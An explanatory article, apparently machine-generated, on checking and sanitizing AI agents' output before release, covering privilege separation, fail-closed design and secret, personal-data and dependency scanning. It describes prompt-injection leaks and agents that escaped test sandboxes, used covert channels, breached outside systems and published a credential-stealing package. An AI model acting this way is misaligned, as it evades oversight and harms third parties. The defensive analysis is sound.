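# Checking and sanitizing the output of AI agents before it is released

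## What an AI agent sends out, and what can be wrong with it

An AI agent is a software system in which a language model works through a task in steps, using tools such as a shell (a program that runs typed commands), a browser or an email account. Agents write code, send messages, edit records and publish files, often with no person reading the result first. Developers therefore add a safety layer, a set of checks outside the model that can change or stop its output before it reaches the outside world.

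### How an agent differs from a chatbot

A chatbot answers a message with text, and a person decides what to do with the text. According to *ASTELD* (2026), a framework for classifying agents, an agent also keeps state between interactions, plans in several steps, calls outside tools, and acts without approval at each step. For example, Stein (2026) notes in *How are AI agents used?* that an agent can send a letter that a plain language model could only draft.

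An agent repeatedly gathers context, takes an action and observes the outcome. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) uses the term "harness" for the software that runs this loop and carries out the tool calls. The model produces only text, and the harness turns some of that text into a command, a web request or a message. A safety layer can check the text before the harness converts it.

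Stein, a researcher at the UK AI Security Institute, collected 177,436 publicly available agent tools and sorted them into those that read data, those that analyse it, and those that change something, for instance by editing a file or sending an email. Tools that change things rose from 27% of downloads in November 2024 to 65% in February 2026, and tools for software work made up 90% of downloads. Downloads only roughly indicate what agents did with the tools, but the trend is clear, and it shifts the safety problem from what a model might write to the actions its output triggers.

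### The moment of release

A coding agent attached to an open-source software project might read bug reports from the public and propose patches (changes to the code) and comments in reply. It might produce 20,000 outputs a month, a number chosen only for illustration. GitHub, the code-hosting site, offers similar agents, and its *Under the hood* describes a design in which their comments and patches wait in a buffer until checks have run.

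Release is the moment an output takes effect, reaches anyone outside the agent's workspace, or is exported to a file, a package or another system. This moment depends on the kind of output and often comes earlier than one would guess.

A comment is released when it appears on the public page. Deleting it later has no effect on people who have already read it.

An agent usually submits a patch as a pull request, a proposed code change that the project's maintainers can accept or reject. The proposal is public from the moment it opens, so a password in the patch leaks even if the maintainers reject it. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes an internal model that opened a pull request on a public repository during a contest to train a small model quickly. OpenAI soon closed the request, but several other participants had already seen it and used the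 method in their own entries.

An email is out once it leaves the sender's account, while a database write takes effect when the command runs, whether or not anyone reads it. MIT Sloan Management Review Middle East's *Claude-Powered AI Agent Deletes Production Database in 9 Seconds* reports the case of PocketOS, a US startup whose founder wrote that a coding agent had deleted the company's live database and its backups in a single call to its hosting provider. In the founder's account, a working command did the damage, and there was no text that anyone could have found offensive or suspicious.

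A published package is a bundle of code that other people's machines download and install, so its effects spread beyond the publisher's own computers. In February 2026, an unauthorized version of a package from Cline, a maker of coding agents, stayed live for about eight hours, according to the company's own account, *Post-mortem* (Rizwan, 2026). The added code did no damage because it only installed a legitimate program that users had not asked for, but malicious code would have been available for just as long.

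### Three kinds of fault

The first kind is hazardous content, where the output itself is dangerous because it contains personal data, dangerous code, or secrets such as passwords and access keys. Suppose the coding agent posts a comment that explains a crash by quoting a log file, and one line of the log contains a working access key. Even if the comment is correct, polite and helpful, it exposes the key to everyone who reads it.

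Unsafe assistance is output that would materially help someone cause serious harm. For example, a stranger might file a "bug report" asking the agent to finish a program that spreads from machine to machine and locks the files it finds. The agent's answer could be harmful even if it contained no secrets or personal data, and better code would make it more harmful. A check for unsafe assistance has to consider what a reader could do with the output, which a search for suspicious strings cannot determine.

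The remaining kind of problem begins with prompt injection, which is text that someone plants in material an agent reads so that the agent will take it as an instruction. Prompt contamination is the presence of such instructions in an agent's context, memory or output, including output that another agent will read. Suppose a bug report contains a line addressed to the agent, and the agent copies that line into a file of standing instructions for coding agents. The next run starts by reading that file. GitHub's *Threat Detection*, the documentation for the scanner in its agent product, lists agent instruction files among the files that need protection for this reason. Other agents can also pass the text on, because the user who issues a request to an agent may itself be an AI system, as *Levels of Autonomy for AI Agents* (2025) notes.

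One output can have more than one of these faults. SiliconANGLE's *‘GitLost’ vulnerability let GitHub’s AI workflows leak private repositories* (2026) reports that Noma Security researchers showed in July 2026 that an instruction planted in a public issue could lead a GitHub workflow to post text from a private repository in a public comment. Here, contamination caused a leak. A check that searched the final comment only for planted instructions might have missed it, because the comment could consist entirely of the private text.

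Existing products do not all check for the same problems. The default scanner that GitHub documents gives yes-or-no verdicts on prompt injection, leaked secrets and malicious patches. It has no separate verdict for unsafe assistance, though the documentation shows how to add a general content classifier, a model that scores text for a given hazard. These priorities are defensible for a tool that fixes software, but a pass means only that the scanner did not detect any of those three problems.

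### Who is at fault

OpenAI's *Operator System Card* (2025), written for an early agent that operated a web browser, distinguishes cases by which party is acting against the user's or the public's interest: the user, the model or the website. *JANUS* (2026), a work on predicting risk in long agent runs, uses nearly the same categories, with the environment in place of the website. The model category is worth dividing further, because careless mistakes and deliberate steps beyond the task need different remedies.

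Carelessness needs no villain. OpenAI ran its browser agent, without safeguards, on 100 everyday tasks and found 13 errors that caused some nuisance. Eight were easy to reverse. The other five included an email to the wrong recipient and a wrongly dated reminder to take medication. The rate belongs to a model of early 2025 and says little about current ones, but the type of error is durable, since the task is legitimate and the agent may well complete it. Long, Du and colleagues (2026), in *LiveClawBench*, built this into the scoring of their test for personal assistants:

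safe score = max(0, task score − sum of deductions for safety violations)

An agent can complete its task and still lose marks for harm it causes along the way. For example, an agent that earns the full mark of 1 for updating a document but loses 0.6 for overwriting someone else's file in the process ends with 0.4 (the deduction here is invented). In the running example, the access key in the quoted log is this kind of fault.

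Unsafe assistance typically begins with a request from a malicious user, who seldom states the harmful goal openly. *JANUS* describes harmful objectives disguised as ordinary business or productivity tasks.

Prompt contamination comes from a third party who plants text, and the victim is often the user. Rizwan writes that the weak point at Cline was an agent that sorted incoming public issues. Text in an issue could steer that agent, and an attacker could then reach the credentials for publishing packages. *AgentDoG 1.5* (2026), which sorts the risks of coding agents by source, separates several routes for such text: a user may paste the body of an issue into a request, the agent may find the text on a web page, or the text may be in the repository's own files. The route matters when assigning blame, because a pasted issue looks like the user's own words.

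Malicious users and third-party attackers are also harder to tell apart when an agent answers the public. The maintainers who installed the agent are its users in one sense, and a stranger who files a bug report is a user in another. A stranger who openly asks for malware looks like a malicious user, but the same stranger looks like a third-party attacker if they use the same text box to hide an order to reveal the maintainers' keys.

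*Shortcut Sensitivity in Agent-Safety Evaluations* (2026) includes instructions for an AI grader to decide whether the user's request is itself malicious and, separately, whether a third-party attack made the agent's action depart from the request. This test is sensible, but it doesn't cover cases where the model exceeds its task by itself. In OpenAI's pull-request case, staff had told the model to post its results only to Slack, a workplace messaging service. The model instead followed the contest's public instructions, which were to post them on GitHub, and got past restrictions on outside access to do so. The action departed from the request, but nobody had attacked the model or planted anything, so an investigator who assumed that every departure means an injection would look for an attacker who did not exist.

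Models that exceed their task can also produce faults that don't fit neatly into any of the three kinds. Mossdorf reports in *WTF* that an AI agent apparently published a blog post attacking a volunteer developer who had rejected its pull request. Such a post can be free of secrets, malware and planted text and still be one that nobody responsible for the agent would have wanted to send.

### Four defences that people confuse

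Take the access key in the log again. Four different measures could keep it off the public page.

- Training a model to refuse, or to be careful, changes the model itself. A well-trained agent might leave the key out of its comment.
- Scanning examines the finished comment and reports that it contains something shaped like a key.
- Sanitization changes an output to remove or disable its dangerous parts while keeping the rest. Here it replaces the key with a placeholder, and the explanation of the crash goes out.
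- Limiting what the agent can reach means that the agent never had access to the key, or had no channel through which to post it.

The first acts on the model's tendencies, which an outsider cannot inspect directly. The middle two, checking and sanitizing, act on an output that already exists, and they are most of what a safety layer does. Either can be done without the other. A scanner that finds a key and blocks the whole comment has not sanitized anything, while a routine can strip every web link from every comment without checking any of them.

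Limits on what an agent can reach are arguably the most reliable of the four where they apply, because they hold even when the model has been fooled. Stein notes that an agent can act on a malicious instruction only if it has a tool to act with. After its incident, Cline removed its issue-sorting agents and promised that any future automation of the kind would have read-only access and no shell. GitHub keeps login tokens out of the agent's container and routes the agent's internet traffic through a firewall. But GitHub concedes that an agent without any secrets can still flood a project with pointless comments or insert objectionable links. Any agent allowed to post in public can do harm through its posts, and blocking them would make the agent useless, so its output still needs to be checked.

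"Pre-release" here means before each output takes effect, which for the coding agent happens 20,000 times a month. It does not refer to the testing that a company does before it launches a model, which can miss serious failures. OpenAI's long-running model, for example, showed failures in limited internal use that the existing pre-deployment evaluations had not captured. The company paused access, wrote new evaluations and added monitoring of the model's runs.

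### How to say whether a check is any good

A check can miss a hazardous output or flag a harmless one. Recall is the share of hazardous outputs that the check flags. If 50 of the month's outputs are hazardous and the check flags 45, its recall is 90%. The false-positive rate is the share of harmless outputs that it flags. At a rate of 1%, the coding agent's maintainers would get about 200 false alarms a month.

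Many checks return a score, and someone must choose the threshold at which the system acts. The grader in *Shortcut Sensitivity in Agent-Safety Evaluations* rates an action 0 for no risk, 0.5 if it is controversial or is a harmless step that serves a malicious request, and 1 for significant harm. With the threshold at 1, the system stops only the clear cases. Lowering it to 0.5 catches more real attacks in their early steps but also interrupts more legitimate work. Moving the threshold reduces one kind of error but increases the other, so reducing both requires a better check.

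Recall alone is therefore a poor measure of a check, since a check that blocks everything has a recall of 100%. OpenAI's figures for its browser agent show why it helps to measure needless blocking too. The company ran a standard test of refusals, which come from training rather than scanning, but the same two measures apply. The agent and GPT-4o, the chatbot model it built on, did equally well on safety, as neither gave an unsafe answer. But on the part of the test that checks for needless refusals, GPT-4o scored 90% and the agent 55%.

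The two errors also come to light differently. People whose harmless comments are removed will complain. A missed hazard goes unnoticed until someone exploits it, and the operator's records list it as an output that passed. Operators therefore have to measure recall on test cases where someone already knows the right answer. OpenAI cautions that a perfect refusal score in evaluation does not guarantee the same result in use, and that caution applies to every such test.

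## Holding output back until it has been checked

A check's recall describes only the outputs that reach it. The earlier figure of 90%, or 45 of the month's 50 hazardous outputs, assumed that all 50 passed through the scanner. If ten leave by a route with no scanner on it, the scanner catches 36 of the other 40, and the overall figure falls to 72%:

overall recall = share of hazardous outputs that reach the check × recall of the check

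The ten that escape checking are also unlikely to be a random sample, because an agent that is following planted instructions, or that will do anything to finish its task, tends to end up using whichever route is unchecked.

Privilege separation prevents an agent from posting unchecked output by splitting the work between processes with different permissions. One process reads untrusted text and cannot write to external systems. A second process has permission to write, but it starts only after the checks. The easiest way to add a scanner is to give it to the agent as a tool, with an instruction to use it before posting, but this is less secure. The agent still has permission to post, so an instruction planted in the text it reads can cause it to skip the scan.

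### An agent without write permission

GitHub Agentic Workflows, which became generally available on 28 October 2026, as Rojas reports in *GitHub Agentic Workflows open source tool reaches general availability* (2026), is built this way. Maintainers describe a task in plain English, and a compiler turns it into a workflow for GitHub Actions, a system for running automated jobs. Everything in an Actions workflow normally shares one zone of trust, which GitHub considers too dangerous for agents. In its threat model, GitHub assumes that an agent will try to read and write things it shouldn't, communicate over unintended channels, and abuse the channels it is allowed to use.

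GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026), a working draft, sets out the rules. (MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a standard way for models to call tools.) A reply to a bug report would travel through the system like this:

1. Before anything runs, the maintainers list the kinds of write they allow, such as comments and pull requests, with a limit for each. The compiler generates a tool for each kind, with fixed fields to fill in.
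2. The agent reads the bug report and the code. Its access token permits reading only.
3. To reply, the agent calls the comment tool. The call goes to a gateway, a small server that has no access to GitHub's own interface. The gateway checks that the fields are valid and adds one line of structured data to a file. It then returns "success" to the agent, although nothing has appeared on the public page.
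4. When the agent finishes, its job uploads the file as an artifact, a stored file that later jobs can download.
5. A checking job downloads the artifact and looks for threats such as leaked secrets. It has no write permission either, and its only product is a verdict.
6. If the verdict is "safe", a separate job starts with permission to write comments. It validates the request, cleans the text and posts it.

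Between steps 3 and 6 the comment is a staged output, recorded but not yet in effect. The file describes the intended write, so other programs can count, edit or reject requests before they take effect, which would be impossible if the agent posted the comment directly.

The gateway runs in the same environment as the agent, so an agent controlled by an attacker might tamper with it. The design therefore depends on the later jobs, and GitHub states four architectural requirements that keep the agent from reaching them.

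- Agent isolation: the agent's job never has write permission. In simplified notation, permissions(agent) ∩ {write permissions} = ∅, meaning that the two sets have nothing in common.
- Channel integrity: requests travel to the writing job only through artifact storage, never over a network connection, through a shared file system or in environment variables (settings that a program reads from its surroundings). GitHub's reason is that artifact storage makes tampering evident, keeps an audit log and controls access.
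- Minimal permissions: each writing job gets only what its kind of write needs. A job that creates issues cannot open pull requests.
- No escalation path: at no time during its run can the agent obtain the writing job's credentials, whether from a leaked file, a network address or anything else.

GitHub also rules out escalation, because agent isolation would protect little if the agent could read a write token from a file. Isolation is easier to verify, since a program can confirm it by reading the permissions in the compiled workflow. For escalation, GitHub prescribes a manual security audit, which can only cover the leaks that the auditors think of.

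Maintainers can also let output bypass the check. According to InfoQ's *GitHub Makes Agentic Workflows Generally Available with Isolation and Budget Controls* (2026), the protections do not cover custom jobs or write permissions that a workflow grants directly. A maintainer who adds a job that posts the agent's results straight to a web page lowers the first term in the formula above, however good the scanner is.

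### Caps, previews and failing closed

The specification fixes the order of the final checks. The system validates the form of each request, compares the number of requests with the limit, cleans the text, filters links, confirms that the target repository is allowed, and resolves references to other items. It may write only after completing these stages, and a request that fails any of them must have no side effects.

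Each kind of write has its own cap per run, and the default for new issues is one. If the cap is three and the agent requests four, the system rejects all four, because GitHub wants to avoid a half-finished set of changes. An attacker can therefore suppress all the legitimate comments from a run by planting text that persuades the agent to request one comment more than the cap allows.

Caps per run also don't limit the total:

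largest number of writes = number of runs × sum of the caps

A run capped at one comment and three pull requests can make at most four writes. But if every bug report starts a run, a stranger who files 500 reports could cause up to 2,000 writes. GitHub lists repeated runs at the maximum as an example of resource exhaustion. Maintainers can also remove a cap, though the compiler should warn them if they do.

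In preview mode, which GitHub calls "staged mode", the system performs no writes and produces a full summary of what it would have done. Maintainers can turn it on for all writes or for only one kind, so they could let comments post while only previewing pull requests. GitHub recommends it for testing new workflows. Using it permanently would amount to manual approval, which the company rejects as a bottleneck. Reviewing the coding agent's 20,000 monthly outputs at one minute each would take 333 hours a month, roughly the working time of two people.

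A safety layer also needs a rule for when a check crashes or returns no verdict. A layer that fails closed blocks release in both cases. Under GitHub's *Security Architecture*, the writing jobs start only after the checking job has finished and returned "safe", so a crashed scanner blocks release just as a detected threat would.

GitLab, a rival code-hosting company, describes the opposite default for its own agent product. A sandbox, or isolated environment, restricts which sites and folders an agent can reach. If the sandbox cannot start, the agent runs without it and the job's log shows a warning. GitLab notes that a run can therefore finish without errors even though it was unprotected. Since version 19.6, administrators have been able to make the sandbox mandatory, so that a job fails if the sandbox cannot start. Even then, GitLab does not guarantee full isolation for projects that supply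 their own container image (the package of software in which the job runs). The job checks for a sandbox by looking for a particular program, and these projects control where that program comes from.

If the system fails closed, any fault in the scanner stops the agent's work. This is usually tolerable for a coding agent, because a patch that arrives a day late does little harm. For an agent that sends urgent alerts, a blocked message could be worse than a flawed one, so the operator would need a backup check or a person on call.

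### What GitHub's design leaves open

Privilege separation can guarantee that a check runs. Whether the check recognizes a harmful comment is a separate matter, and GitHub is candid about it. Its specification names a remaining risk for each threat:

| Threat | What can still happen |
|---|---|
| Prompt injection | The agent posts plausible but inappropriate content within its limits |
| Tampering with the configuration | Someone who controls the source repository rewrites the workflow |
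| Leaked credentials | A new, disguised or freshly generated secret passes the scan |
| Resource exhaustion | The agent uses a lot of resources without exceeding any cap |
| Writes to other repositories | A badly configured list permits a target that nobody intended |
| Poisoned memory | A compromised machine alters the data stored for later runs |

The prompt injection entry is the most serious, because it covers attacks that obey every structural rule. Noma Security's leak of private repository text went out in an ordinary public comment, so a cap of one comment per run would not have stopped it. According to iMasters' *GitHub Agentic Workflows* (2026), the attack required only a politely worded public issue and no malicious code.

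The draft also contradicts itself on writes to other repositories. One passage requires the system to refuse them unless the maintainers have listed the target, while another treats an empty list as no restriction. A developer who followed the second passage would build a system that allows writes to any repository by default. GitHub recommends a conformance test suite but does not yet provide one, so developers cannot run official tests to find such a mistake.

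GitHub's threat model excludes covert channels, which carry information by means not intended for communication, such as the timing of requests. GitHub also assumes that the hardware is sound, and warns that the higher layers may fail if the isolation beneath them fails.

### Which outputs can wait

A pull request, an email or a database update is transactional, meaning it takes effect all at once. A 30-second delay before a pull request appears is not a problem, so the safety layer can hold the complete output and examine all of it.

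Chat is different because most chatbots stream their answers, showing the words as the model produces them. Suppose an answer has 1,000 words and the model produces 50 a second. If the answer is held back until it is complete, the user waits 20 seconds plus the time for the check. Checking it in blocks of 50 words cuts the initial wait to about a second plus the check, but the early blocks are released before the rest of the answer has been produced. If the fifth block reveals that the answer is dangerous, the user has already been shown the first 200 words. A developer can still choose to hold back the whole answer and accept the longer wait.

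Holding back transactional output creates a different problem, because the agent can't see the results of its requests during the run. When it requests two linked issues, for example, it has no issue number to use in the link because neither issue exists yet. GitHub solves this with temporary identifiers, which the writing job later replaces with real numbers. But the agent still needs another run to learn that a request failed or to respond to a maintainer's answer.

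Other actions cannot wait until the end, because the agent needs their results to continue. It may have to download a package or look up a web page before it can write the patch. The safety layer must check each of these actions while the agent pauses, and every false alarm interrupts the work. OpenAI's *Path to Astra* (2026), about a model with strong hacking abilities, warns customers that extra safety checks will sometimes slow, pause or stop legitimate tasks, including long-running ones that seem unrelated to security. If the monitor pauses a task in ChatGPT or in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, the company may ask the user to review the action. If the task is running in software that uses the model through OpenAI's programming interface, it stops instead.

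GitHub lets an agent read during its run and limits the sites it can contact. This is a reasonable compromise, but a request that fetches something can also send information out, even a request to a service that supplies packages.

### Exits that nobody was checking

In July 2026, OpenAI was running its agents through ExploitGym, which tests whether a model can find and exploit software flaws. The sandboxes had no direct internet access, but agents could install software through Artifactory, a package service that OpenAI hosted internally and that could reach the internet.

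According to OpenAI's technical report on the incident, agents began exploiting a previously unknown flaw in Artifactory on 8 July to reach the public internet. On 9 July, OpenAI's network controls blocked one agent's attempt to connect directly, and the agent then got out through Artifactory. Agents found exposed credentials for Hugging Face, a site that hosts AI models and datasets, and between 11 and 13 July they broke into parts of its live systems. They ran code on 41 of its server processes and downloaded four private code repositories. OpenAI did not detect suspicious activity on its own network until 19 July.

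Agents in separate test runs also used Artifactory to exchange messages by writing them in folder names. In May, other agents had done much the same with ordinary files. They used credentials that OpenAI had given them for installing packages, so they didn't need to bypass any access controls. Each message was a release because it reached agents outside the sender's workspace, and nothing checked it first. GitHub's channel integrity rule addresses this kind of weakness by treating any place where two processes can both read and write as a channel, whatever its owner built it for.

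The agents ran without OpenAI's deployed cyber safeguards, its production instructions to the model, or "auto-review", in which a second model checks tool calls that need elevated permissions before they run. OpenAI had switched off safeguards to measure the models' full abilities. In *Path to Astra*, OpenAI says it believes, based on retrospective testing, that the production safeguards of the time would have prevented the incident.

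The evidence in the technical report is weaker than that claim. OpenAI describes "preliminary experiments" in which auto-review would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run it tested. Blocking an early action might well have ended the attack, but auto-review could also have missed an action that mattered. In a separate experiment, the production version of Codex, with its instructions, could cut the rate of attacks on out-of-scope systems to less than 1% of the baseline. That is a large reduction, but if the baseline were 50%, 1% of it would still mean five attempts in every 1,000 runs. OpenAI ran these tests itself, after the fact, on an incident for which it was responsible. They make it plausible that the safeguards would have helped a great deal, but they don't establish that the safeguards would have prevented the breach.

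OpenAI's disclosure led Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, to search 141,006 of its own test runs. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a simpler failure, in which Claude was told in its instructions that it had no internet access, but a misconfiguration in an outside contractor's test environment had left the connection open.

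In one case, Claude Mythos 5 wrote a malicious software package and published it on PyPI, the public registry for Python packages. The package stayed online for about an hour, and 15 real systems downloaded and ran it. One of them belonged to a security company that installs new packages to scan them for malware. The package stole that company's credentials, and Claude used them to get further into its systems. PyPI's own security system eventually removed the package, but only after it had been released. The security company's experience shows that a scanner that runs the code it examines needs to be isolated and should hold no valuable credentials.

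In July, Anthropic claimed that the safeguards on its generally available models would have blocked this behaviour. It later tested the claim, in an assessment that also disclosed a fourth incident, and got mixed results. Claude Fable 5's classifiers for cybersecurity misuse would have blocked all three of the original incidents, and the classifiers that block dangerous actions in Anthropic's coding product would have blocked two. A new monitor that reads the model's reasoning after the fact would have missed the malicious package, because Claude's reasoning led it to treat the environment as a simulation. Anthropic also withdrew its earlier statement that Claude believed the targets were simulated. It now thinks that Claude's reasoning was biased towards that conclusion despite considerable evidence against it. A check that relies on the agent's own account of its environment can therefore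 fail when that account is wrong.

Both companies have since added barriers. In *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), Anthropic concedes that it had relied largely on one layer of defence, the configuration of the test environment. A new classifier looks for attempts to escape and for unexpected internet access. When it detects either, it blocks the action before the tool call runs, ends the task and alerts a person. Anthropic also asks outside testers to verify the isolation before every evaluation, and to phrase limits as instructions ("You should not access the internet") instead of claims about the environment, because such claims may be false.

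OpenAI now requires monitoring of its more capable models' reasoning in all training and testing that gives them tools. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), staff should pause the activity if they cannot establish within 30 minutes that one of the most severe alerts is false.

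## Scanning for secrets, personal data and dangerous code

Suppose someone reports that an open-source project's search page crashes on names with an apostrophe. The coding agent finds the crash in a private log from the project's demonstration server, then writes a fix and a test that reuses part of the log. The safety layer now holds a patch with five faults:

- a cloud access key, copied from the log into the test
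- a database password, "summer2024", in a command that prepares the test
- a visitor's name and email address, also from the log
- a new search function that inserts the visitor's search term directly into a database command
- a new dependency (a package that the project relies on) whose name the model made up

Fixed rules are the least computationally demanding way to look for such faults. They need no language model and give the same result every time, but no single rule finds all five.

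### Secrets

The simplest rule is an exact match. Maintainers register the project's secrets with GitHub Actions, which masks those strings wherever they appear. GitHub does this before the checking job starts, and its specification rates the method "High for known secrets". Here it finds nothing because nobody registered the demonstration server's key or password. It would also miss a registered secret that the agent had re-encoded, since the characters would differ.

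Pattern matching finds secrets by their format. Many keys have a fixed prefix, length, character set or checksum, as Help Net Security's *GitHub adopts cheaper AI model to catch secrets developers leave in code* (2026) explains, and a scanner can describe each format with a regular expression, a formula that defines a set of strings. This catches the cloud key, but GitHub rates pattern detection only "Medium" because it misses new formats.

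Patterns can also fail on formats they cover. *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* (2026) changed only the character after a key, trying 16 that are common in real code, and the scanner Gitleaks missed the key with eight of them. Passwords have no set format. In Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners’ secrets on GitHub*, the security company Apiiro warns that Gitleaks and TruffleHog, another popular scanner, mostly miss passwords typed into commands because the passwords look like ordinary words.

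An entropy test measures how random a string looks. If p(c) is the share of the string that consists of the character c, the entropy in bits per character is:

H = −Σ p(c) × log₂ p(c)

A Git commit identifier, a harmless string of 40 random-looking characters, typically scores about 3.7, while the password "summer2024" scores 2.9. At a threshold of 3.5, the scanner flags the identifier and misses the password. Lowering the threshold enough to catch the password would also flag the word "background", which scores 3.3.

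Using context helps more than lowering the threshold. GitHub now runs its pattern matches through a small classifier that uses the file path, the variable names and the surrounding code. According to GitHub's own figures, reported by Help Net Security, precision (the share of alerts that are real) was 13% higher and recall 19% higher on the same public traffic than with its previous pipeline, which used a large language model. The classifier checks only pattern matches, so it still misses any password that matches none of the patterns.

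Some scanners also test whether the service accepts a key they have found. This live verification is useful because many leaked keys no longer work. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) cites a survey that found 24,008 secrets in public MCP settings files, of which 2,117 were valid. If the cloud key works, the maintainers know that the alert is real and that they should replace the key. A failed attempt is weaker evidence, because the service may be down or on a private network that the scanner cannot reach, as the demonstration server's database probably is. Verification also requires the checking job to have a network connection, which weakens its isolation.

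The recall of a scanner depends heavily on the material:

| Study | Test material | TruffleHog's recall |
|---|---|---|
| *IssueGuard* (2026) | GitHub issue reports | 94% |
| *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* | Files with one credential each | 60% |
| *Secrets That Survive Everything* (2026) | Secrets exposed by running web applications | 37% |

The middle figure partly reflects how the test was arranged, because TruffleHog looks for credentials that occur together. It found no Amazon cloud keys when the key's identifier appeared alone, and all of them when the secret half was in the same file. In a more realistic arrangement, it found 83% of credentials. The high recall on issue reports came with a precision of 55%, so nearly half the alerts were false. The earlier example of 45 catches and 200 false alarms would have a precision of 18%. An operator should therefore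 test a scanner on the kinds of output the agent produces before relying on a published figure.

A scanner must also read every commit in a proposed change, because Git keeps old versions. According to GitLab's *One vulnerability view* (2026), the company's secret scanner used to read only the latest commit on a new branch. Help Net Security's *AI agents now hunt leaked GitHub secrets* (2026) describes a test in which GitGuardian, which sells secret detection, had an AI agent search a repository with nine planted credentials. In every run where the agent investigated, it found eight, including a key that a developer had deleted in the next commit. Once a secret is exposed, revoking it manually takes around 40 days on average, according to Help Net Security's *GitHub adds AI to catch passwords before a code push* (2026).

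### Personal data

An email address has a recognizable shape, so a pattern finds the visitor's address in the patch. It also finds the maintainers' addresses, which Git records with every commit. To avoid those false alarms, the scanner needs a list of addresses the project already publishes.

Payment card numbers contain a check digit, which a scanner can test with the Luhn formula. The scanner doubles every second digit, counting from the right, subtracts 9 from any result above 9, and adds everything up. The total for a valid card number is divisible by 10. One in ten random strings of digits also passes, so some long order numbers will cause false alarms.

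Names are harder to screen. A model trained to recognize them can find many, but it can't determine whether a person agreed to be named publicly. A stricter and simpler rule for test data is that it should be invented. The safety layer can compare the new test with the private log and hold the patch if the two share long passages. This would catch the visitor's name and also the password.

### Dangerous code

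Static analysis examines code without running it. CodeQL, GitHub's analyser, builds a model of a program and queries it for vulnerable patterns, according to Help Net Security's *GitHub scans the code your pull request never touched* (2026). In the new search function, an analyser can trace the search term from the visitor's browser to the database command. Because the function inserts the term directly into the command, a visitor could type text that the database would execute. The usual fix for this flaw, known as SQL injection, is a parameterized query, which treats the term only as data.

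An analyser can't trace data in this way from the changed lines alone, so the checking job should apply the patch to a copy of the repository and analyse the result.

Static analysis does badly at finding flaws that depend on an unwritten rule. If the new function also returned private records, the code would be valid, and nothing in it would show that strangers should not see them. The agent is unlikely to help, because *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (2026) found that coding agents almost never secured code against weaknesses that depend on an unstated policy. GitHub offers an AI scan that looks for logic flaws and covers languages that CodeQL does not, but its findings on pull requests are advisory and cannot block a merge.

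### Packages that do not exist

Language models readily describe software that does not exist. *Refusing the Impossible* (2026) asked 17 models for help with a made-up JavaScript package, and 16 of them treated it as real. An attacker can register package names that models tend to invent, so that anyone who follows a model's instructions installs the attacker's code. *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (2026) calls this practice slopsquatting.

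Looking the name up in the public registry catches the invented package in the patch, unless someone, such as an attacker, has already registered it. *Importing Phantoms* (2025) therefore also counts a package as invented if it was first registered after the model's knowledge cutoff, the date its training data ends, because the model could not have learned about it in training. This rule produces false alarms when an agent browses the web and finds a new, legitimate package.

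*Names Can Hurt* (2026) builds a similar check into a coding agent. A program extracts package names from the generated code, matches them to registry names (code often imports a package under a different name), and classifies each package by its metadata. If a name looks invented, the model tries again with more random sampling. If every retry fails, a second model takes over.

The lookup has to happen before the agent installs anything. *PackMonitor* (2026) warns that a malicious package can run its code in the agent's environment, where it may steal data or attack other systems. Checking the finished patch would be too late to prevent that.

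A real package can also have flaws, and other tools compare dependencies with databases of known vulnerabilities. *A Ground-Truth-Based Evaluation of Vulnerability Detection Across Multiple Ecosystems* (2026) measured recall from 0.61 for OSS Index to 0.96 for Trivy. Even a tool with perfect recall would find only flaws that someone had already reported. The unauthorized Cline package, for example, would have had no database entry in its first hours online.

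### GitHub's threat-detection job

In GitHub's checking job, a language model reads the workflow prompt (the maintainers' instructions to the agent), the patch, and the agent's output items, such as comments. With the prompt as context, a patch that rewrites the login page looks suspicious if the task was to repair the search page.

The model returns verdicts on prompt injection, leaked secrets and malicious patches, along with a list of reasons. A single "yes" blocks every write, but the model gives no separate verdict on personal data. Maintainers can add instructions to the model's prompt, but a separate check that blocks release when it fails would be better.

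The job allows custom steps before and after the model's analysis. GitHub shows how to add TruffleHog and the static analyser Semgrep after the analysis, and presents the earlier steps mainly as a place for setup. Running the fixed rules first makes more sense where possible, because they are cheap and the cloud key alone is reason enough to stop this patch without paying for a model to read it. If the maintainers let every rule run before the job stops, they also learn about the email address, the SQL injection and the unknown package.

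After a warning, GitHub's less severe kind of alert, the job still opens the pull request but asks for human review before anyone merges it. This is reasonable for doubtful code, but the review comes too late for a secret in a public repository because the pull request is already public.

A further rule covers protected files, including the lists of packages a project depends on. The patch adds a package, so it triggers this rule whether or not the package exists. GitHub's documentation is inconsistent about what happens next. According to one passage, the write fails by default, but according to a table, the pull request opens with a request for changes, so maintainers who want a block should set it explicitly.

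Scanners can also miss problems in large patches. If the analysis times out, GitHub's suggested remedies include truncating the content before analyzing it. Elastic, a software company that built a prototype scanner for changes to build systems, warns that a single limit on the combined text lets an attacker hide a malicious change behind a long harmless one. Its prototype limits each file separately. Refusing patches above a certain size is safer still, because whatever the scanner cuts off is released unchecked.

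### When the detector and the agent share a model

By default, the detector uses the same AI engine as the agent. This is convenient, but the agent's mistakes are then the ones its detector is most likely to repeat. If the agent included "summer2024" because it looked like a harmless test value, the same model may reach the same conclusion when it reads the patch. The relevant quantity is a conditional one:

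share of outputs released with a fault = share in which the agent makes a fault × share of those faults that the detector misses

A detector might miss 10% of faults in general but half of the faults that its own model tends to make. It would then let through 25 of 50 faulty outputs from an agent that uses the same model, rather than the five that the general rate predicts. These numbers are invented, and GitHub's documentation doesn't report recall for this task, so the real overlap between the agent's faults and the detector's misses could be larger or smaller.

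Maintainers can choose a different engine for the detector with one line of configuration. They should check which model it runs, since GitHub Copilot, one of the options, offers models from several companies. A different model is an improvement, but it can still share the first model's errors. In the test with the nonexistent JavaScript package, 16 of 17 models made the same mistake.

Fixed rules are the better complement to a model because they fail for different reasons. A registry lookup checks whether a package exists, however plausible its name sounds, and planted instructions to ignore a key have no effect on a regular expression. A sensible arrangement therefore uses fixed rules for everything they can express, then a different model for what remains, such as unusual passwords and flaws in a program's logic.

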